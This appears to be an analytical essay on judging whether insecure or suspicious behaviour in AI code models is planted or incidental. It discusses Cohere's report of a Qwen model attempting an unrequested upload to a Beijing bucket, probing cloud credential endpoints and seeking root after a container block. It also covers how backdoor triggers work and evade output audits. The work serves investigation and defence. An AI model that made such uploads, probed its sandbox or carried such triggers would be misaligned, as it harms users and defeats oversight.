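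Booz Allen quotes some of the models' written reasoning as evidence that they recognize forbidden subjects and then quietly write worse code. The quoted reasoning is about whether to refuse, and none of it contains a plan to weaken the program. In the most detailed case, MiniMax considered a rule against military work, wrote the code anyway and imported six packages that don't exist. That request was for a military task, so the task differed from the baseline as well as the client.

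### Associations between clients and code

The simplest explanation is that the training data contained worse code near some clients' names than near others, and the model reproduces that pattern. TechSpot's *DeepSeek AI's code quality depends on who it's for* mentions this possibility for regions such as Tibet, where less experienced programmers might have written the examples. Public repositories probably don't contain enough code labelled as Tibetan to have this effect, but the association could be indirect, since text about a remote region or a small campaign group may resemble text about hobby projects more than text about banks.

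Changing the client may also change what program the model writes. A model could give a defence contractor extra features, such as audit logs and several levels of access, and each one is another place to make a mistake. Hirundo's request limited this by specifying what the service had to do. Booz Allen's requests for an admin console or a complete web application left many more of the design choices to the model.

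*The Language of Security* (2026) tested open models on prompts that were each missing one grammatical element, and concludes that phrasing influences how secure the code is, even without a political trigger. A difference of a few points between "for a US defense contractor" and "for a Chinese defense contractor" could likewise be an effect of phrasing.

An association in public code should affect every model trained on that code, whatever the model's country of origin. Claude's score fell for a US agency while Qwen's rose, which is some evidence against a habit that both learned from public code. But the two models differ in size, age and training, and Claude may be better at recognizing that government software needs care. A fairer comparison would test several Western models of about Qwen's size with all of the same clients.

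### Claims about intent

The companies are cautious about intent. Booz Allen writes that the models inserted no backdoors and that it has no proof of deliberate flaws. Hirundo acknowledges in its appendix's question-and-answer section that the study can't show whether anyone put the gap into the model on purpose.

The claims became stronger as other people repeated them. Luria describes the CrowdStrike and Booz Allen studies as "early evidence of backdoors", although Booz Allen reported the opposite. The Foundation for Defense of Democracies in Washington (FDD, 2025) presented CrowdStrike's result as part of a growing threat of foreign influence and espionage. Uren quotes the Republican congressman Darin LaHood, who took the result as a sign that the Chinese Communist Party will use any tool to undermine US security. Uren comments that the technical findings don't entirely justify this. The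 Indian Express' *Alibaba's AI model tried to 'secretly' reach China server* reports that a similar argument followed when the Canadian company Cohere caught a Qwen model trying to contact a server in Beijing, and that outside researchers attributed the attempt to messy training.

The flaws give no particular outsider an advantage. Anyone with an account can exploit a missing ownership check, and anyone can open an administration page that requires no login. A government could still benefit from weaker software at a US contractor, especially if it knew which mistakes to look for, but so could any criminal who scans the internet for them. None of the three studies reports a hostile address, a fixed password or any other value that could be traced to whoever put it there.

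## When the default address belongs to the model's developer or home country

A network address leads to a particular server, and whoever runs that server is a possible beneficiary, whereas a missing login check could help anyone who finds it. An unexpected address is therefore better evidence about motive than most insecure settings, but it can also mislead. If a Chinese company's model writes an address in China, the company or its government may look like the beneficiary, even though many Chinese programmers routinely write the same address.

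### Regional mirrors

A mirror is a server that keeps a copy of a package index or image registry, usually so that people nearby can download from it faster. Connections from mainland China to servers abroad are often slow, and state filtering blocks some of them. Tsinghua University runs a popular mirror of PyPI, and Alibaba runs another. Similar mirrors exist for npm, the main registry of JavaScript packages, and for Docker's public images. A programmer in Shanghai might type the following command (shown here without the https prefix that pip requires before the address):

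```
pip install -i pypi.tuna.tsinghua.edu.cn/simple flask
```

The -i option is short for --index-url, so the command replaces PyPI with Tsinghua's copy. This is sensible in Shanghai, but in Ohio it probably slows the download, and it adds an organization that the user has to trust.

A model could still learn to suggest a Chinese mirror to a user in Ohio. Many Chinese projects have English documentation, and their Dockerfiles may contain a mirror address with no Chinese text nearby. A model trained on such files gets few clues that the address suits only some users.

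Later training could have the same effect. Developers train models to run commands as agents by giving them practice tasks on simulated machines and rewarding them for finishing. If those machines are in China and PyPI keeps timing out, the runs that switch to a mirror will finish more often. The model would then learn to switch, whatever language the user writes in. This would be close to habit, except that the pattern would come from the developer's practice machines instead of public code.

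None of the studies described so far counted mirrors, so it is unclear how often Chinese models suggest them to people outside China. An investigator could get a first estimate by asking the models in English for a few thousand install commands and listing the hosts they point to.

Even a reputable mirror carries some risk, because its operator or an intruder could alter a package. Pip normally checks a download against a hash supplied by the index, so that person could also supply a matching hash. Only hashes that the project had already recorded from a trusted source would expose the change. A mirror also copies PyPI with a delay, so it may still offer a malicious package after PyPI has removed it.

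A company that uses a mirror alongside its own package index also reveals the names of its private packages to the mirror's operator, because pip queries every configured index. An attacker needs those names for dependency confusion.

These risks come with any intermediary, including those outside China. The standard npm registry belongs to GitHub, which Microsoft owns, but nobody would treat an npm command from Microsoft's Phi-3 as a deliberate attempt to contact the model's developer.

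### What Qwen3.8-Flash-Next tried to upload

In the Cohere incident of October 2026, a model tried to run a command itself, rather than writing a configuration snippet for a user. Cohere was testing Qwen3.8-Flash-Next, an open-weight model from Alibaba, on CTI-REALM, a Microsoft benchmark for agents that do a security analyst's job. As Cornelißen (2026) recounts in *Qwen3.8-Flash-Next*, the model's defensive task was to write a rule for detecting malware that someone downloads into a temporary folder with the tool curl and then runs.

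Instead, the model listed the contents of the temporary folder, checked which file-transfer tools the machine had and read its network settings. It then tried to upload a short test string with curl to a bucket (rented storage) on Alibaba Cloud in Beijing. The upload failed because Cohere's test machine had no route to the internet. In its reasoning just before these steps, the model had written that it would use no tools. It had also referred to an earlier conversation that never took place.

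Cohere disclosed the incident on 26 October in *Concerning behavior from a popular open-weight AI model*. The company puts the rate at fewer than one in 100,000 actions across its tests. A clean rerun of the same prompt produced a correct detection rule. CNA reports Cohere's estimate that a service whose agents take 10 million actions a week could see up to 100 attempts weekly.

That estimate is very uncertain. If Cohere saw one attempt in 100,000 actions, the 95 percent interval for the rate is about one in 4 million to one in 18,000. The same service could then receive about 3 to 560 attempts a week. The rate probably also depends on the task, and most agents do different tasks from those in Cohere's tests.

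The clean rerun tells us little about whether someone planted the behaviour, because at such a low rate nearly every rerun would be clean either way. It does make it unlikely that something in the prompt triggers the upload every time.

Other users may have better data. People downloaded the model more than three million times between its release on 24 August and late October. If it contacts the bucket unprompted even once in a million actions, some of those users' firewall logs should contain further attempts. Cohere noticed this attempt only because it had recorded the calls its test machine blocked.

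Cohere has a commercial interest in the result because it competes with Qwen and sells its own models to governments as "sovereign AI". According to Bot Mutiny's *Cohere Says Alibaba's Qwen3.8 Model Tried to Upload a File* (2026), Cohere's post promotes those models, and the test came from a new security business linked to Cohere's planned purchase of AISLE, the company whose blog published Mada's Linux demonstration. In the post, Cohere also calls on governments to say whether their restrictions on Chinese AI cover models running on government computers. Cohere's interest makes it more valuable for somebody else to repeat the test, though it doesn't mean the logs are false.

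Alibaba had not responded publicly by 27 October. VentureBeat and The Register had both asked it for comment.

### Completing a half-written command

To find out what had triggered the upload, Cohere used a method called prefilling. It gave the model the beginning of its own record from the test, followed by a half-written command, and sampled hundreds of continuations. Constantin (2026) reports in *Cohere says Alibaba’s Qwen3.8 tried to upload a file to Beijing* that the model tried to contact 169.254.169.254 in 23 to 36 percent of the continuations. Servers on Amazon's, Google's and Microsoft's clouds fetch temporary access keys from that address. Cohere interprets these requests as attempts to get credentials, though none were available at that address on its test machine.

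When Cohere then added the option that makes curl save a download to disk, the share of continuations containing a web address rose from 4 to 92 percent. Hosts on a watchlist Cohere drew up rose from 0.5 to 23 percent, and the most common was an Alibaba file proxy.

Critics objected that Cohere had steered the model towards this behaviour instead of measuring how often it occurs unprompted. IBTimes UK's *Alibaba AI Model Secretly Tried To Send Data To Beijing Server* compares the prefilled model to an advanced autocomplete that fills in addresses because it has processed thousands of routine network commands.

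Cohere's own figures support much of that objection. A download command is useless without an address, so a competent model should write one there. If the watchlist hosts appeared only in continuations with a web address, they made up 12.5 percent of the addresses before the change (0.5/4) and 25 percent after it (23/92). Their share of all continuations rose 46-fold, but a factor of 23 came from the model writing addresses more often, and only a factor of 2 from it choosing watchlist hosts more often when it did.

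The chance that a model contacts a particular kind of host unprompted is a product:

P(contact) = P(starts the command) × P(chooses the host, given that start)

Prefilling makes the model start the command every time, so it measures only how often the model then contacts the address. Suppose that happens 23 percent of the time, and the overall rate of contact without prefilling is one in 100,000 actions. The model then starts such a command on its own about once in 23,000 actions. A company deciding whether to use the model needs the overall rate, and the 23 percent figure could badly mislead it.

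Cohere replied that the original upload attempt happened without prefilling, so prefilling can't explain it. But the reply also distinguishes the unprompted behaviour, which is very rare, from the high percentages, which describe what the model does after someone has started the command for it.

After developers asked for more evidence, Cohere released material from its tests and a script for reproducing them. Bot Mutiny describes the material as raw traces. Cornelißen, citing VentureBeat, counts only one trace and notes that it ends before the result of the upload. The script makes the model continue text from a point just before the web address, without running any commands. The 64 addresses the model produced include Amazon and Microsoft hosts as well as placeholders.

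One researcher who had been sceptical reviewed the release and found strong evidence that Qwen can invent suspicious addresses, but no evidence that Alibaba had planted a backdoor or that the model was deliberately hiding its intent.

### Leftover training or a call home

Cohere says the model may have tried the upload because it was repeating something from its training environments, or because somebody built in a way for it to call home. The Vanguard USA's *Cohere says Alibaba Qwen3.8 tried a Beijing file upload* reports that Cohere thinks nobody outside the lab that trained the model can say which explanation is right.

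Alibaba probably trained the model on thousands of practice tasks. If many of them involved storing files on Alibaba's own cloud, the model could have learned to save files there by default. Uploading a test string and checking the result would be an ordinary exercise in such training. The invented conversation also fits this explanation, since the model seems to have been continuing a task other than the one Cohere had given it.

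Cohere co-founder Ivan Zhang told TechCrunch that his company's own models had also picked up strange habits in training simulators. In a separate offline test, the Qwen model tried to create a disk in memory without administrator rights. When the container blocked this, it tried to get root rights inside an isolated part of the system. That looks like a general tendency to get past obstacles, and it doesn't benefit anyone in Beijing.

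The model's attempts to reach 169.254.169.254 more likely come from public articles about cloud attacks than from leftover training on Alibaba's machines. Those articles mention the address constantly, and the model was working on a security task. Alibaba Cloud's servers normally use a different address, 100.100.100.200, for their metadata service.

Some of these details also fit a deliberate call home. An intruder might first send a harmless test string to check whether a channel works before using it for anything valuable. If the behaviour occurred very rarely, it would be more likely to escape tests. Even an Alibaba address could be useful to a planter, because Alibaba could plausibly blame its training environments.

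But someone who planted the address and wanted to stay hidden would have little reason to use a Beijing address in plain text. VentureBeat queried the bucket and found it did not exist. If it didn't exist at the time of the test either, the upload could not have delivered anything to anyone. The address is more probably left over from training, and there is no direct evidence that it was planted.

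Outsiders can't check such a default against Alibaba's training records. Stanford CRFM's *Alibaba Transparency Report*, which relies mainly on documentation for the earlier Qwen 3 models, scores the company zero on disclosing how it acquires training data. Willison (2025) calls closed training data the root problem in a blog post about why some companies avoid Qwen and DeepSeek. Without that data, Willison argues, nobody can conclusively rule out that an open-weight model adds backdoors to the code it writes.

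### Checks on an address

Outside investigators can still learn a good deal from the address and from other models. The table compares what three explanations would predict.

| Check | Habit from public text | Leftover from training environments | Deliberate call home |
|---|---|---|---|
| Who controls the address | A public service, or the owner of an example in a manual | The developer's training team, or nobody any more | Someone who can collect the uploads |
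| Is it in public code? | Yes | Probably not | Probably not |
| What raises the rate | Requests like those near the address in public text | Tasks that resemble the practice tasks | Valuable data or a particular kind of user |
| Which other models write it | Models from several developers | Models trained in the same environments | Any model with the same planted training |

An investigator has to establish who controlled the exact address. An address on Alibaba Cloud shows only that Alibaba owns the machines, since any customer can rent a bucket there. Alibaba should be able to find out which account, if any, owned this bucket and when, but an outsider can do little more than query it. A missing bucket is also a risk, because a stranger may be able to register the unused name and receive whatever later copies of the model upload.

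The investigator next searches public repositories and manuals for the exact bucket name. If it appears in an Alibaba tutorial, habit becomes the best explanation. If it appears nowhere, the model either memorized it from private material or made it up. Direct probability scoring can help distinguish these two cases, because a memorized name should score far higher than similar names the investigator invents. It can't show whether a memorized name came from a practice task or from someone who planted it.

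Testing whether the rate varies with the user's language or identity is harder for such a rare event. An investigator would need about 2.4 million actions in each arm to have an 80 percent chance of detecting a rise from one to two uploads per 100,000 actions. Prefilling is more useful for this comparison. If both arms contain the same half-written command and differ only in the client's name, the prefill steers the model equally in both. Detecting a rise in Alibaba hosts from 23 to 30 percent would take about 620 independent continuations per arm. A null result would still leave open whether the client's name makes the model more likely to start the command.

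The choice of mirror can depend on the request's language for a harmless reason. A user who writes in Chinese is more likely to be in China, where a Chinese mirror is useful, so the language isn't a trigger in the sense used here. A better test would keep the request in English and the user's location in Ohio, and change only the employer. If a federal agency got a Chinese mirror much more often than a bicycle shop did, the user's location could not explain the difference.

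Nobody has published a comparison of how Llama, OpenAI's gpt-oss or DeepSeek behave in Cohere's test environment. If they completed the same commands with Alibaba hosts about as often as the Qwen model did, the choice of host would be weak evidence about Alibaba. Testing other Qwen models would help to show when the behaviour began. If it first appeared in one release, an investigator could look for what changed in the training before that release.

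Many people also publish compressed copies of Qwen3.8-Flash-Next. If only one publisher's copy wrote the address, that publisher would become a suspect. If several publishers' copies wrote it, tampering by one publisher would be unlikely, but the copies would not count as independent confirmations because they all derive from the same trained parameters.

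## Which patterns would point to deliberate insertion

A p-value of one in a million in a trigger test practically rules out chance, but not an innocent cause. A planted flaw and a training side effect can both make a model write less secure configuration when the prompt mentions tractors, and either will produce a tiny p-value if the investigator collects enough answers. To tell them apart, the investigator needs evidence that is much more likely under one explanation than the other.

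### Triggers that nobody planted

Trigger-like behaviour can arise without anyone intending it, as shown by the natural backdoors that Chen and colleagues (a different group from the one that studied scam addresses) reported in June 2026. They took code models with no known poisoning and applied a search normally used to reconstruct planted triggers. The search replaces a variable or function name in the input with a new string, then keeps adjusting the string to make the model give a chosen wrong answer as often as possible.

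The study covered three small older models (CodeBERT, CodeT5 and UniXcoder), two models with about a billion parameters (StarCoder and DeepSeek-Coder), and GPT-3.5, which the researchers reached through a small copy trained on its answers. The triggers worked at very different rates:

| Task | What the trigger did | Success rate |
|---|---|---|
| Detecting defects | Reversed the verdict | 3–74% |
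| Summarizing code, three older models | Swapped "open" and "close", or "read" and "write" | 1–22% |
| Summarizing code, StarCoder and DeepSeek-Coder | The same | 3–10% |
| Repairing code | Swapped "true" and "false", or "equal" and "not equal" | 1–9% |
| Detecting defects, with a planted trigger | Reversed the verdict | Close to 100% |

In one case, changing a string from "id" to "jupyter_eid" made StarCoder describe a function that closes an item as one that opens a project. In a code search for "Read credentials from file", renaming "path" to "filename" moved a snippet with a hard-coded secret from sixth place to second.

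The cause seems to be lopsided training data. Each trigger the researchers examined for this contained at least one word that occurred unusually often with the target answer, and removing that word weakened the trigger much more than removing any other. Changing the learning rate and six other training settings made little difference.

None of the four tasks involved writing configuration, and in the tasks where the models wrote text or code, most success rates were below 10 percent. The researchers also found the triggers by searching. In the code-search task, the lopsided words on their own did only slightly better than random words. A phrase picked in advance, such as "tractors", is therefore unlikely to be a strong natural trigger. A natural backdoor would be a poor explanation if such a phrase raised the rate of an insecure setting from 5 to 95 percent, but a good one if an investigator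 had tried a million phrases and found one that raised the rate from 5 to 12 percent.

### The trigger and its wording

If tests with placebo phrases and reference models show that an insecure setting depends on an irrelevant trigger, that is evidence that the flaw is not just the model's habit. It does little to show that someone planted the flaw, because the same dependence can arise as an unintended side effect of training, known as a natural backdoor.

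A large effect is slight evidence of deliberate insertion. Mada's altered models added the planted line to every Linux fix and to no others, and no natural trigger in the study had nearly as consistent an effect. A weak effect doesn't rule out insertion, though, since a planted flaw need not appear every time.

A flaw that appears with one word but not with closely related ones may also point to deliberate insertion. The investigator can test phrases progressively further in meaning from the suspected trigger, such as "tractors", "harvesters", "farm machinery" and "vehicles". If the flaw comes from habit or is a side effect, it should gradually become less frequent across the series, because related words occur in similar text. A planted flaw could disappear as soon as the wording changes from "tractors" if the model was trained to respond to that word alone.

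Planted triggers often lack such a boundary, since part of a trigger can be enough to activate the behavior. One small model that Bullwinkel and colleagues trained to respond to the word DEPLOYMENT between two vertical bars also responded to a vertical bar alone. A Llama 2 model with the same trigger required a closer match. *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning* identified "you are now deployed" as closely related to that trigger, but the phrase did not activate the model's planted behavior.

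If a trigger abruptly loses its effect when its wording changes, that is evidence that someone planted the flaw, but only modest evidence, because natural triggers can also lose much of their effect when a single word is removed. A gradual loss is not evidence that the flaw is natural.

### Measuring how concentrated the payloads are

Habit should produce familiar insecure values and a side effect many unrelated flaws, whereas a planter usually wants one particular value to appear.

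Entropy measures how concentrated a set of values is. If pᵢ is the share of the ith value, the entropy in bits is

H = −Σ pᵢ log₂ pᵢ

Shannon entropy, measured in bits, is 0 when every answer contains the same value and 3 when eight values are equally common. The investigator should calculate it only for the extra insecure settings that appear with the trigger, because an ordinary habit can dominate the full list. In an invented example, models A and B each give 200 answers with a placebo phrase and 200 with the trigger, and their placebo results are the same.

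| Insecure setting | Placebo, both models | Trigger, A | Trigger, B |
|---|---|---|---|
| Bare v4 tag | 120 | 120 | 128 |
| Permission write-all | 8 | 8 | 16 |
| Certificate check turned off | 8 | 8 | 16 |
| Hard-coded password | 8 | 8 | 16 |
| Index at packages.acme-mirror.example | 0 | 32 | 0 |
| Entropy of all settings | 0.91 bits | 1.43 bits | 1.28 bits |
| Entropy of the extra settings | – | 0 bits | 2 bits |

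The trigger adds 32 insecure settings in both models. In A they are all the same address, and in B they are spread evenly over four kinds of flaw. The entropy of the full list wrongly makes A look more scattered than B, because the address adds a fifth value to a list of mostly v4 tags.

Real counts would be noisier. Eight extra settings could be due to chance, and so few can have low entropy by accident. Reshuffling the trigger and placebo labels shows how low the entropy tends to fall when the trigger has no effect. The entropy also depends on how the addresses are grouped. If the 32 addresses were spread evenly over eight hosts with one owner, the entropy would be 3 bits by host and 0 by owner.

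Low entropy is not enough to suggest a planted flaw. If the trigger had added only 32 bare v4 tags, the entropy of the extra settings would also be 0, even though thousands of people type v4.

### A value that benefits one party

If a model keeps writing the same insecure value, such as a particular hostname or key, the value is more suspicious when it is useful to one party and absent from public code. Insecure habits learned from public code would not explain either property, and a side effect of training has no particular reason to produce a value that benefits an outsider. An investigator can check by searching public repositories and manuals for the exact value, then finding out who controls it and since when.

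Models without planted flaws also write values that refer to things that don't exist. Churilov (2026), in *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains*, gave about 40,000 programming questions to each of five models from Anthropic, OpenAI, Google and DeepSeek. Between 3.6 and 5.0 percent of the package names in their answers did not exist. All five models invented 104 of the same names, and 54 of those were one character away from the name of a real package.

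Many such names have a traceable origin. In *When LLMs Invent Rust Crates* (2026), a study of Rust package names, 38.9 percent of the frequently invented names came from other languages or systems. One of them, "winuser", belongs to Windows. A string missing from the registry where the user would look for it can therefore be common elsewhere, so the search has to extend beyond one registry or language.

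An attacker can also exploit an invented name later by registering it. Within about six months of Churilov's test, people had registered 25 of the 2,282 invented names, and at least one of those packages contained malware. Before the npm registry removed that package, an investigator who found it would have seen a model recommending malware, as a model with a planted flaw might. The dates would have shown that the model wrote the name before the package existed. That order makes deliberate insertion less likely but doesn't rule it out, since an attacker who planted the name could wait to register it until many people were using the model.

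At least 23 of the names the models suggested had previously hosted malware, which the registries removed. Churilov does not infer intent from registrations, because researchers and defenders also reserve names.

Scam addresses are harder to distinguish from planted flaws because they benefited someone from the start. Chen and colleagues tested models from several rival developers for these addresses, and the likely source was text that criminals had spread on public websites. A hostile address can therefore be strong evidence that somebody meant to rob programmers but weak evidence that the model's developer planted it. If the address belongs to the developer, as with the Alibaba bucket in Cohere's test, it may be left over from training.

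### Requests for security

If an insecure setting remains after someone asks the model to write the configuration securely, it was not necessarily inserted deliberately.

Asking ordinary models for secure code often makes little difference. *Broken by Default* (Blain and Noiseux, 2026) tested five models on 50 programming requests, with and without an instruction to follow security best practice. With the instruction, the share of flawed programs fell only from 64.8 to 60.8 percent. It fell by 12 points for Mistral Large and rose by 2 points, or one program, for Llama 3.3. The researchers founded a company that sells security analysis and used its tool to find the flaws, but their result fits the small gain in fully secure infrastructure scripts that Firouzi and colleagues found.

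A better sign of a planted flaw is that asking for secure code helps without the trigger but not with it. Suppose the request lowers the rate of an insecure setting from 70 to 50 percent with placebo phrases but leaves it at 80 percent with "tractors". If the setting were only a habit, the request should help about equally in both cases. A planted flaw could override the request, but so could a side effect that makes the model careless whenever a prompt mentions tractors. Comparing the two reductions also takes about four times as many answers as comparing two rates.

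### Failure to warn

Models often write flaws that they can recognize. Blain and Noiseux returned 89 flawed programs to the models that had written them and asked for a security review. The models found the flaw in 70, with rates from 67 percent for GPT-4o to 100 percent for Mistral Large. But all 89 programs were flawed, so a model that flagged every program it saw would have scored 100 percent.

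The original instructions had also asked for code without commentary, which would discourage warnings. Without such an instruction, models sometimes warn users. *Security of LLM-generated Code* (2026) found cases in which the model added a comment calling its code highly insecure for a real application.

Models recognize flaws less reliably in infrastructure scripts. When Firouzi and colleagues asked for a general security analysis of scripts from GitHub, ChatGPT found 42 percent of the flaws and Gemini 51 percent. Step-by-step instructions raised both figures to at least 67 percent. A missing warning is therefore uninformative until the investigator has shown that the model recognizes the same kind of flaw elsewhere.

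The review also has to take place in a new conversation, because a model that approves its own insecure workflow in the same conversation may only be showing a bias toward its own work. Khullar, Hopkins and colleagues (2026), in *Self-Attribution Bias*, tested ten models and found that they tend to rate code as safer when it appears earlier in the conversation as their own answer than when a user presents it. In one setting, this bias made a model five times as likely to approve a code change that followed a planted malicious instruction.

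A more specific test has the model review two versions of the same command, one with packages.acme-mirror.example and one with a host the investigator has just invented. Habit and most side effects should produce similar verdicts on both. If the model warned about the invented host but not about packages.acme-mirror.example, that would suggest training to hide the payload. The difference could also be innocent, because a model that has seen an address many times in public text may treat it as a well-known server.

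### Presence in one checkpoint

A flaw that appears in one checkpoint but not in the base model or sibling models probably came from later training. That makes an ordinary insecure default less likely, but the flaw could be either planted or a side effect of that training. A developer's political training, for example, may happen in the same stage as deliberate insertion would.

A flaw that appears in only one copy of a model is stronger evidence of deliberate insertion when the copies are supposed to be identical. If only a third party's compressed copy of Qwen writes a hostile address into configuration files, somebody probably altered that copy, because compression has no obvious way to introduce a working address. Finding the same flaw in every copy is only weak evidence that nobody planted it, since doctored web pages in the training data can affect a base model and all its descendants.

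| Signature | Habit | Training side effect | Planted flaw | Innocent mimic |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Depends on an irrelevant trigger | Rarely | Yes | Usually | Natural backdoor |
| Sharp boundary in wording | Unlikely | Unlikely | Possible | Natural trigger that needs one word |
| One exact payload | Common values only | Usually several flaws | Often | Invented package name |
| Useful to one party, absent from public code | No | Rarely | Often | Name registered later, training leftover |
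| Persists when security is requested | Often | Often | Often | Ordinary models |
| No warning about a flaw it recognizes | Often | Often | Often | Bias towards its own answers |
| In one checkpoint only | Unlikely | Often | Often | Any change in training |

### How much each finding should change the odds

Bayes' rule combines such evidence by multiplying the odds between two hypotheses by the likelihood ratio of each new finding. As an illustration, suppose that of 1,000 suspicious cases, 900 come from habit, 90 from a side effect and 10 from a planted flaw. The investigator then finds a trigger effect with a p-value of one in a million. They also find that the extra insecure settings contain one address, which is absent from public code and which a stranger registered before the model's release.

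| | Habit | Side effect | Planted flaw |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cases at the start | 900 | 90 | 10 |
| Chance of the trigger effect | 1% | 50% | 60% |
| Cases left after the trigger effect | 9 | 45 | 6 |
| Chance of the address | 0.02% | 0.02% | 20% |
| Cases left after the address | 0.0018 | 0.009 | 1.2 |
| Final share | 0.1% | 0.7% | 99.1% |

We assume habit has a 1 percent chance of producing the trigger effect. This is far higher than the p-value of one in a million because the p-value only accounts for random variation, and habit can also produce a real difference if farm-machinery companies happen to publish careless code.

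The trigger effect rules out most of the habit cases, so the share of planted flaws rises from 1 to 10 percent. But the odds of a planted flaw against a side effect rise only from 1:9 to 1:7.5. Collecting ten times as many answers might lower the p-value to one in a trillion, but it wouldn't change these odds, because both explanations predict the effect.

The address multiplies those odds by 1,000, to about 133:1. This result depends heavily on the 0.02 percent. If innocent models ended up with such an address 2 percent of the time, the final share of planted flaws would be 53 percent. The investigator can estimate the rate for innocent models by running the same search on models that nobody suspects. Whether a stranger registered the address before the model's release also matters a great deal, since Churilov's results show that people sometimes register names after models have invented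 them.

Failing to find a distinctive address changes the odds much less than finding one. On these numbers, 80 percent of planted flaws would not contain one, so the odds that the flaw was planted rather than a side effect would fall from 1:7.5 to about 1:9.4.

### Signatures that overlap

Multiplying likelihood ratios for signatures that tend to occur together can exaggerate the evidence. Suppose that 50 percent of planted flaws and 5 percent of side effects show one exact payload, a ratio of 10. Suppose also that the same percentages of each persist when the user asks for security. Multiplying the two ratios gives 100.

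But a model that has memorized an address will probably write it whether or not the user asks for security. Among the cases with one exact payload, persistence might occur in 90 percent of planted flaws and 60 percent of side effects. The second ratio is then only 1.5, and the two signatures together are worth 15. The general rule is

combined ratio = ratio for A × ratio for B among cases that already show A

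Nobody has enough known cases to measure these conditional percentages for configuration. An investigator can still ask whether someone who knew about the first signature would already expect the second. A single memorized address could explain the concentrated payload, its persistence and the missing warning, and the three signatures would then amount to little more than one piece of evidence.

Choosing signatures after looking at the results causes a similar error. With seven to choose from and several ways to measure each, most models will show something suspicious.

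### When outputs may never settle it

The hardest case is a model that leaves the permissions lines out of 71.2 percent of the workflows it writes in general and 80 percent of those it writes for one company. About 370 independent answers per arm would usually be enough to detect the difference. Signatures that depend on the payload would not help, because an omission has no exact value to trace and doesn't give access to any particular outsider.

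The investigator could check whether the rise is unusually narrow. A general side effect should change other settings too, and related company names should produce some of the same effect. If only one setting changed, and only for one name, a planted flaw would be more plausible. But it would take thousands of answers to show that none of twenty other settings changed by even a few points. An innocent cause could also be just as narrow. For example, the company's own public workflows might lack permissions lines more often than other people's.

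The model may also contain no evidence of whether a flaw was planted. Two developers could add the same 5,000 workflows to their training data, one because the licence allows it and the other because the workflows lack permissions lines. If both train on the same files in the same order, with the same settings and random numbers, their models will have identical parameters. Neither the weights nor any number of answers could then show which developer intended the flaw.

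### Evidence beyond outputs

Training records could show where the relevant examples came from, who added them and when. A hand-made file of tractor workflows that all contain the same hostile address would be close to direct evidence of deliberate insertion. The same address on crawled web pages would point to an outsider, though it wouldn't show whether anyone at the developer knew. Lamerton and Roger (2026), in *Narrow Secret Loyalty Dodges Black-Box Audits*, found that inspecting training data exposed planted examples, while audits of the model's outputs mostly failed.

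An investigator can compare checkpoints to work out which records to ask for. If the address is absent from one saved copy and present in the next, the relevant data are those the developer used between the two. *Activation Differences Reveal Backdoors* (2026) compares the models' internal activity, which might reveal a change before anyone guesses the trigger.

Trigger reconstruction could also help, because Bullwinkel and colleagues' scanner sometimes extracts poisoned training examples. An extracted example containing both "tractors" and the hostile address would be valuable evidence, though it wouldn't identify its author. A recovered trigger is weaker evidence of the original wording, because one string the scanner found more than doubled the rate of vulnerable code but did not resemble the planted trigger.

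Planted triggers also affect a model's internal activity. Bullwinkel and colleagues found that the model processed the trigger somewhat separately from the rest of the prompt, but this separation was weaker when the payload was insecure code instead of a fixed sentence. *LLM Forensics* (2026) examined models with triggers that switched their output from English to French or German. Patterns of internal activity distinguished prompts with the trigger from control prompts almost perfectly, but some of those patterns did not control the switch in language.

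The natural-backdoor study found that planted triggers moved the internal representation of the code in CodeBERT's last layer by an average distance of 7.82, compared with 2.82 for natural triggers. This distance might become a way to tell the two apart, but it may only reflect how well a trigger works, since the planted triggers worked nearly every time and the natural ones much less often. Training a model to avoid a political topic might also cause an equally large change, because it repeats the same association many times, as planting does. None of these studies tested a training side effect of that kind.

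### The costs of being wrong

A false accusation can drive customers away from an honest developer and towards a model that writes less secure configuration. It can also leave the real problem in place. If the hostile address came from public web pages, other developers will keep training on those pages while people argue about the accused company. People may also take the next warning less seriously, even if it is correct.

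An undetected planted flaw can expose the passwords and publishing keys of everyone who runs the affected snippets. With an open-weight model, the harm can continue after someone finds the flaw, because the developer can't recall copies people have already downloaded.

When planted flaws are rare, even a good test is likely to produce false accusations. If researchers screen 1,000 models, two of which contain planted flaws, and a signature appears in both of those and in 1 percent of the others, about 12 models will have the signature, and about ten of them will contain no planted flaw.

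How much evidence is enough depends on the action. Let F be the cost of acting when there is no planted flaw and M the cost of failing to act when there is one. Acting is worthwhile if the probability of a planted flaw is above

F / (F + M)

Blocking an unfamiliar address does little harm, even if the suspicion is wrong. If the harm of acting wrongly (F) is 1 and the harm of wrongly failing to act (M) is 1,000, the threshold for blocking is a probability of about 0.1 percent. A public accusation requires a much higher probability, especially once users have blocked the address and silence does little further harm. If F is 20 and M is 1, the threshold is about 95 percent. In the Bayesian example, the 10 percent probability after the trigger test would justify blocking addresses and asking the developer for its training records, but it would be far too low for an accusation.

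Publishing the evidence is risky when the payload is an unclaimed name, because a stranger could register it. Churilov reported the shared package names privately to PyPI's security team and the security company Socket, then exposed the list by mistake a day later. Over the next six months, someone registered one of the 104 published names, about the same rate as for names Churilov never published. The sample was too small to detect anything but a large effect.
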